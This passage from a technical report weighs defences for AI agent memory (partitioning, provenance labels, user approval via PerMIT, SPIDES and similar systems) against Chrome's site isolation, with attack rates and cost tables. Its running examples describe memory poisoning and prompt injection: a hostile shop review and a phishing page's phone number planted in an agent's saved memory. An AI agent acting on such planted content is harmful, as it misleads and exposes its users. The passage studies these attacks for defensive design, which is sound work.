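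The attackers knew the host's instructions and memory design, and software refined each email through up to 40 rounds of testing, so the rates apply to well-prepared attacks. The rates vary a lot between models. When another group ran the benchmark on searchable history without a defence, the attack succeeded in 80% of cases against Kimi K2.5 and in none against Claude Sonnet 4.6.

### Choosing a partition key

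Suppose the host saved four things from the laptop task: the delivery address from the mail, the price comparison, the user's stated preference for quiet machines, and a false claim by a reviewer at Shop A that Shop B refuses returns. A month later, the user asks the agent to buy a monitor from the better of the two shops. What the agent remembers depends on how the host divides the saved memory.

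| Partition key | What it blocks | What it breaks |
|---|---|---|
| Site | The reviewer's claim doesn't load when the agent visits only Shop B or the bank | The address stays with the mail site, and the comparison belongs to no single site |
| Task | Nothing from the laptop task returns, including the false claim | The user has to repeat the preference, and the agent has to find the address again |
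| Project, such as "home office" | Memories from other projects, such as medical appointments, stay out | The false claim returns along with the useful entries |
| Tool server | Mail stays out of tasks that use other tools | The address is unavailable at the shops, which share one partition because the agent reaches both through the browser |

A host could also key agent memory by a pair, as browsers do with storage. A browser pairs the top-level site, which indicates what the user is doing, with the embedded origin, which indicates whose data it is. The closest equivalents for an agent would be the project and the source. Data from Shop A would then be stored in one partition for the home office and another for the user's medical purchases, so the agent would be less likely to mention one while working on the other. The agent would still need an exception to use the address from the mail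 at a shop.

As with MCP servers, separate stores don't help much if one model reads them all. If the agent loads both shops' memories to choose between them, the false claim can still influence how it judges Shop B. *AgentSys* (2026) protects the main agent's working memory by having separate workers read the tools' outputs and return only short values in a fixed format. Attacks succeeded 0.78% of the time on AgentDojo and 4.25% on a second benchmark. The agent completed 64.36% of tasks with the defence and 63.54% without it. These tests cover memory within a task and don't include stored entries that the agent retrieves weeks later.

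Dividing memory by subject would address a different problem, where an agent brings up private facts even though no attacker is involved. *PersistBench* (2026) assigns memories to domains such as health and finance and counts a failure when an irrelevant memory from another domain affects an answer. The median failure rate was 53%, according to *Mitigating Over-Personalization in LLMs via Structured Memory* (2026). But dividing memory by subject wouldn't separate it by author, so the shop's prices and the hostile review would share a partition.

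### Where the comparison with browser storage strains

A browser can partition a tracker's data without understanding it. The tracking company writes an identifier, only that company reads it back, and the browser never has to combine it with another company's data. The identifier also can't mislead the browser, so partitioning only has to protect the user's privacy. Partitioning an agent's memory also has to protect the agent from being misled by what it recalls.

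Summaries make the boundaries harder to draw. Mem0's second model compares new facts with saved ones, removes duplicates and resolves contradictions. A phishing page's number could therefore replace the bank's real one, leaving an entry about the bank that came from the attacker. *SEAgent*, described in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026), avoids such mixing by keeping past events in a record that its memory model cannot rewrite. The host clears the context after each round, and the model only selects which events to bring back. This preserves the source of each entry, but the agent doesn't get the combined summaries that make long histories manageable.

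Much of the value of agent memory comes from moving information between sites. A user who moves house wants every shop to receive the new address, but has little reason to want an advertiser to recognise them on every site. *Always-On Agents* applies contextual integrity, a standard under which a flow of information must suit the circumstances in which someone shared it. Sending the address to a shop that will deliver a laptop meets that standard and sending the shop a medical note does not, although both would cross the same partition boundary.

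### Labels that survive between sessions

With provenance labels, the host lets memories cross boundaries but records their sources. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) calls the lack of such labels a "cookie problem" and argues that without them, leaks between sessions are the default.

The labels have to last as long as the memory does. *MemLineage* (2026) points out that some earlier systems erase their labels at the end of each run. It attaches labels to the memory entries instead, so an outside source remains on record after a model has rewritten its text. In a test case from *Ghost in the Agent*, an agent saves a confidential revenue forecast and uses it in an internal report three days later. NeuroTaint saves its tracking data at the end of the first session and reloads it in the second, so it can still connect the report to the forecast.

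Over-labelling gets worse as memory accumulates over months. *AgentKernel* (2026) labels each entry separately because one combined label for a whole session would make most memory unusable. With separate labels, the agent could recall the user's preference for quiet machines without treating it as private mail. A summary that drew on both the preference and the mail would still need both labels.

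### Promotion by user approval

Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026), in *PerMIT*, extend the dual-model pattern to memory and let the user decide which hidden entries the agent may use:

1. The host saves everything from web pages, tools and files as untrusted.
2. When the planning model recalls an untrusted entry, it receives only a placeholder. A quarantined model can search the hidden entries but also returns placeholders.
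3. If the task needs the hidden text, the host shows the user the exact text, its source and the user's original instruction.
4. If the user approves, the agent can use that text with the tool concerned, now and in later sessions.

This resembles the Storage Access API, but an approval releases one piece of text, whereas the API gives a frame all its usual cookies. Jiang and colleagues gave a computer-checked proof that every value reaching a sensitive tool is one the user typed or approved for that tool. The proof assumes that the host labels sources correctly and displays values faithfully.

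They tested PerMIT on the benchmark by Das and colleagues, with the hostile text already in memory:

| Setting | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | GLM-5 | Kimi K2.5 | GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Searchable history, no defence | 0% | 10% | 80% | 20% |
| PerMIT, approving every request | 0% | 10% | 10% | 0% |
| PerMIT, always deciding correctly | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| PerMIT, with the agent's own model deciding | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

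For Kimi K2.5, most of the improvement came without anyone rejecting a request. When decisions were correct, three models had higher average task success than with undefended searchable history, but GPT-5.4's fell from 99% to 89%. PerMIT also searches memory differently, so the test doesn't isolate the effect of approvals on task success. No real users took part, and Jiang and colleagues have not yet tested attacks that adapt to the model making the decisions.

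An approval covers a text and a tool, but not a purpose or a time limit. If the host uses one tool to type into all web pages, approving the address for Shop A could also let the agent enter it at Shop B. This is convenient when buying the monitor, but the user might not want the permission to cover every later task.

PerMIT can also do the opposite of partitioning and share approved memories between users. Once enough people or their agents have approved an entry, others can use it without being asked to approve it themselves. In a test with communities of up to 90 agents, where each entry needed ten approvals, none of 12 hostile entries was approved. With so few attempts, the success rate for similar entries could still be as high as 22%, at 95% confidence.

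The delivery address and the false phone number show how the three approaches differ in practice:

| Approach | Delivery address, one month later | Phone number from the phishing page |
|---|---|---|
| Partition by site | Unavailable at the shops | Stays in the phishing site's store |
| Provenance labels | Available, with a check before the agent sends it | Returns with a record of its source |
| User approval | Available once the user approves the text | Hidden until the user approves it |

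The user can easily check their own address but not the bank's number, which they are asking for because they don't know it. Seeing the digits won't help them decide whether to approve the request, so it has to show which site the number came from. Even then, the user has to notice that the phishing site's web address is not the bank's. A host that partitions by site could compare the two in code if it already knows the bank's real web address.

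## What isolation costs in browsers and in agent hosts

Isolation in an agent host can create extra work for users, who may have to approve a delivery address or search the mail for it again because the host keeps each site's memories apart. Browser isolation has drawbacks for users too, but most users never notice them.

### What Chrome users paid

Reis and colleagues measured the overhead of site isolation on people's own computers. For two weeks in October 2018, they compared Chrome users on Windows who had the feature with an equally large group without it. In the table, the 99th percentile represents very heavy use, with around 40 sites open at once.

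| Measure | Without site isolation | With site isolation |
|---|---|---|
| Renderer processes, median | 4.4 | 6.2 |
| Renderer processes, 99th percentile | 35.0 | 52.7 |
| Total memory, median | 610 MB | 685 MB |
| Total memory, 99th percentile | 5,777 MB | 6,274 MB |
| Time until a page first shows content, 25th percentile | 457 ms | 467 ms |
| The same when going back or forward, 25th percentile | 177 ms | 227 ms |

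The number of processes grew by almost half, but total memory grew by only 9% to 13%, because each process held less. Chrome also shares processes where it safely can. A frame joins an existing process if another tab already has one for the same site, and whole tabs from the same site start to share when the number of processes passes a limit that depends on the computer. But one slow frame can then delay or crash others from its site.

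Overall, page loads slowed by at most 2.25%, because Chrome starts the new process while it waits for the network. Going back or forward often loads a page from the cache, with no network wait during which to start the process, and the fastest of these loads slowed by 28.3%. The slowdown would have been 40.7% if Chrome didn't keep one spare process ready for such cases.

The overhead of isolation also depends on how people browse. When Reis and colleagues loaded single pages in an otherwise empty browser, isolation increased memory use by 4% for Google's home page and by 89% for a page that needed ten processes.

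Site isolation let Chrome undo two earlier defences against Spectre, which offset part of the overhead of isolation. Chrome removed compiler changes of a kind that slowed some programs by up to 15%. It also restored a form of shared memory that browsers had turned off, disrupting web applications such as AutoCAD.

### What it took to rebuild the browser

Chrome's developers bore most of the burden of isolation. Over five years, about 350 people changed or added roughly 450,000 lines of code in 9,000 files.

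The most disruptive change was moving frames from other sites into their own processes, because many features had been written for pages that ran in a single process. To find a word on a page, Chrome used to search all the frames inside one renderer. Now the main browser process has to send the search to each renderer and combine the results, without revealing to one site whether another site's frame contained the word. It also has to handle renderers that crash or stop responding. Developers also had to adapt printing, screen-reader support, spellchecking, autofill, zoom and many other features.

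Websites needed few changes. Reis and colleagues received around 20 reports of bugs in the new design, none serious enough to make them turn it off. A few pages malfunctioned because they resized a frame and immediately sent it a message, which could now arrive before the frame received its new size.

Chrome kept sites working partly by accepting weaker isolation. Up to 13.4% of page loads involved a page that changed its origin while running, so the developers separated sites instead of origins. They also let some mislabelled files through. Chrome would have blocked 20% of responses if it had relied on labels alone to block private data from other sites. It blocks less than 1% because it also checks the content.

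Partitioned caches cost network traffic, since a browser may have to download the same font ten times if ten sites use it.

### A gradual rollout

The Chrome team introduced site isolation in stages. In 2017 it first separated browser extensions from the web pages embedded in them, which affected only about 1% of page loads. It then let companies choose a few high-value sites to isolate, and these early users reported at least 24 problems. After that, in 2018, Chrome isolated all sites on desktop computers.

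Isolation was harder on phones because they have less memory and fewer processor cores. Their operating systems also discard background pages, which leaves fewer processes to share. Chromium's Android version, released in September 2019, therefore isolated only sites where users log in. At the time, according to PortSwigger's *Confining untrustworthy code*, the developers had recently fixed several ways to bypass isolation through features such as payments and WebSockets, a type of two-way connection.

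Mozilla started a similar project for Firefox in April 2018, and The Hacker News (2021) reported that the rollout began three years later. Until then, Firefox used up to eight processes for all web content, so pages from different sites often had to share one.

### Costs measured for agent hosts

Researchers have measured the costs of several defences for agents, each against a different baseline.

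| System | Baseline | Measured cost |
|---|---|---|
| SOPGuard | BrowserOS without it, on whole tasks | 2.07% to 5.79% more time |
| ceLLMate | Chrome without it, running a script with no model | 7.25% to 15% more time, about 25 MB of memory |
| INTACT | A planner that reads the whole page in one call | 83.2 seconds instead of 2.5 to plan a task, and lost functionality on 3.7% of tasks |
| SPIDES | The same agent with no defence | 67.1% to 86.1% of tasks completed, compared with 58.2% to 91.1% |

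These percentages can't be used to rank the systems because their baselines differ. SOPGuard's overhead is a smaller percentage than ceLLMate's, for example, because Wang and colleagues timed whole tasks, in which BrowserOS spends much of its time waiting for a model. SOPGuard added 1.2 to 4.6 seconds to tasks that averaged between 33 and 204 seconds. Meng and colleagues timed a script that made 11 moves around GitLab in 13.93 seconds. ceLLMate added about one second with a 100-entry sitemap and two seconds with 300 entries. With a model in the loop, the same delay would be a much smaller share of the total.

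SOPGuard also had no measurable effect on how well BrowserOS did its tasks. Across four benchmarks and three models, scores changed by at most 1.2 percentage points, in either direction. But BrowserOS failed many of these tasks even without SOPGuard. With GPT-5.4 it scored 0.156 out of 1 on one benchmark, which left little room to detect a loss.

### INTACT's slower plans

INTACT is slow because it shows the model one page element at a time. In Iqbal's tests, it made a median of 55 model calls per task, while the conventional planner made one. The median price rose less, from $0.0021 to $0.0045, because the calls share instructions that the model's provider can cache and bill at a discount. The measurements leave out seven pages on which planning took more than 15 minutes.

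Most of the delay comes from making the calls one after another. Iqbal estimates that running them in parallel would reduce the median time to 12.5 seconds and add about $0.0014 per task, but has not built this version.

The 3.7% figure for lost functionality is a rough estimate. A model compared the page elements that each planner chose, and on 40 of 1,091 tasks it rated only the conventional planner's choice suitable. On another ten tasks, it rated only INTACT's suitable. The model could not decide on about a third of the plans, often because the outcome depended on a later page, and the researcher did not execute any of the plans. The gap is wider on another measure, with the model rating 10% of INTACT's plans unsuitable, compared with 4.9% of the conventional planner's.

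### Task completion and approvals with SPIDES

Zverev and colleagues did have agents carry out their tasks, on the MicroNet test sites. The completion rates below combine their results for two types of task, and each rate is based on 280 runs. "Masking" is Untrusted Content Masking, which hides untrusted regions and lets the agent ask only narrow questions about them.

| Model | No defence | SOPGuard | Masking | SPIDES |
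|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91.1% | 93.2% | 67.5% | 86.1% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88.2% | 85.7% | 42.9% | 77.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 88.9% | 90.0% | 56.1% | 82.1% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 68.9% | 66.1% | 58.2% | 69.3% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58.2% | 58.2% | 48.9% | 67.1% |

SPIDES's lowest rate, 67.1%, is therefore an improvement on the undefended agent, while its highest is a loss of five percentage points. The largest loss was 11 points, with GPT-5.6 Terra. The two Opus models did poorly without a defence partly because their provider's safety filters blocked some tasks whose attachments contained passwords or phishing messages. SPIDES avoided some of these refusals by hiding the attachments from the main model. Isolation similarly let Chrome restore shared memory, which another safeguard had removed.

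SPIDES roughly doubled the estimated price of a task, from $0.17–$0.66 to $0.37–$1.42. The estimates exclude discounts for cached input. These amounts are far higher than INTACT's, but INTACT's cover only the planning of steps on a single page, with a different model.

SPIDES needed an average of 1.84 user approvals per completed task, and SOPGuard needed 0.22. But SOPGuard asks for approval less often because it ignores harmful actions within a single site. In another comparison, Zverev and colleagues made each defence ask for approval whenever it could not otherwise match SPIDES's protection, with a limit of eight approvals per task. Under those conditions, SPIDES completed more tasks than SOPGuard or masking with every model.

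INTACT would prompt users less often than SPIDES. Its plans needed the user's consent on only 112 of the 1,091 tasks, and on 58 of those the third party was a service that runs cookie or consent dialogs. But each task took place on one page, so the tasks seldom needed the transfers between sites that SPIDES and SOPGuard check.

In Zverev and colleagues' tests on harmless tasks, the software approved every request immediately. A real user may be away from the screen or refuse a step that the task needs.

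### Why the costs differ in kind

A browser can isolate two sites and still show them together. Each renderer draws its own part of the page, and a separate process combines the parts into one image without letting either site see the other's part. The user reads both and draws any conclusions. Most sites keep working under isolation because they never needed to read each other's private data.

In an agent host, the model reads and combines the sources, so separating them can prevent it from doing what the user asked. INTACT's planner can't compare values in different elements, so it couldn't pick the cheapest laptop from a list of search results. Trail of Bits' rule stops the shopping task at the second shop. CaMeL can combine sources but fails some harmless tasks, partly because its planner can't read what the tools return.

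Other designs keep the combination but require user approvals. In IsolateGPT, for example, emailing one report from a cloud drive may require the user's permission up to four times.

Engineers can reduce memory use and running time, as Chrome's developers did with the spare process and as Iqbal proposes with parallel calls. Faster computers also help. But these improvements don't reduce the time a person needs to read a request and decide whether the address in it is correct.

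### The shopping task with and without isolation

Suppose the agent has opened both shops, the notes application and the email with the delivery address. It has six actions left. It must enter the address and request a quote at each shop, then type the comparison into the notes and save it. The user trusts the operators of all four sites.

| Design | Approvals | What the user loses |
|---|---|---|
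| No isolation | 0 | Protection against a review that makes the agent send a private message instead |
| SOPGuard | 3 | Time spent checking the address twice and the comparison once |
| SPIDES, if the agent reads the address | 6 | Time spent checking every remaining action |
| SPIDES, if the address stays hidden | 2 | The agent's ability to notice that it has the wrong text |
| SPIDES, if the user supplies the address in a labelled note | 0 | The agent's help in finding the address |

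SOPGuard asks about the three entries but not about the clicks that follow.

With SPIDES, the result depends on whether the agent reads the address. Once the agent reads any part of the email, the email's labels apply to the whole context, and none of the six actions passes SPIDES's checks.

If the mail page shows the address in its own element, the agent can copy it into the forms without reading it. The context then stays trusted, and only the two entries need approval. If the user writes a note naming both shops as permitted readers, the entries don't need approval either, but the user has then already done part of the task.

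In the last two cases, the agent must also leave the customer reviews hidden. Otherwise, SPIDES will require approval before every later click on a shop's page.

### Who pays

| System | Host or browser developer | Site owner | User |
|---|---|---|---|
| Site isolation | Five years of engineering | A few repairs | More memory |
| SOPGuard | Tracking labels in the browser | Nothing | Approvals for transfers between sites |
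| INTACT | Recording scripts and planning by element | Nothing | Longer waits, some approvals |
| SPIDES | Tracking labels in the browser | Labels on its pages | A list of trusted sites, approvals |
| ceLLMate | Checking requests | A sitemap and policies | Reviewing the permissions for each task |

The extra model calls also cost money. Under a flat subscription, the vendor pays for them at first, while a user charged by the token pays for them directly.

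Site isolation spread because one company could do nearly all the work and turn it on for everyone. Reis and colleagues write that the Chrome team accepted the extra memory because attacks such as Spectre were severe and the alternatives were weak. Users had no decisions to make, and site owners gained protection without doing anything.

A vendor could ship SOPGuard or INTACT in the same way, since neither requires help from websites. But users would see every approval request and slow task and not the thefts that were prevented, so a competing product with fewer approval requests may look better.

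SPIDES and ceLLMate face a different problem because their protection depends on site owners. A shop gains little from labelling its reviews until popular agents read the labels, but agent vendors have little reason to add that feature while few shops provide labels. Meng and colleagues point out that developers already maintain similar files, such as robots.txt, which lists the pages search engines should skip.

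Agent hosts could try isolation with companies first, as Chrome did. A company controls its internal sites and its employees' browsers, so it can write the labels and ensure that agents use them. Its administrators can also maintain the list of trusted sites so that employees don't have to. A host for the general public could begin with the tasks where theft would do the most harm, as Chrome did on phones, and hide untrusted text only when the agent has access to the user's mail or bank account.
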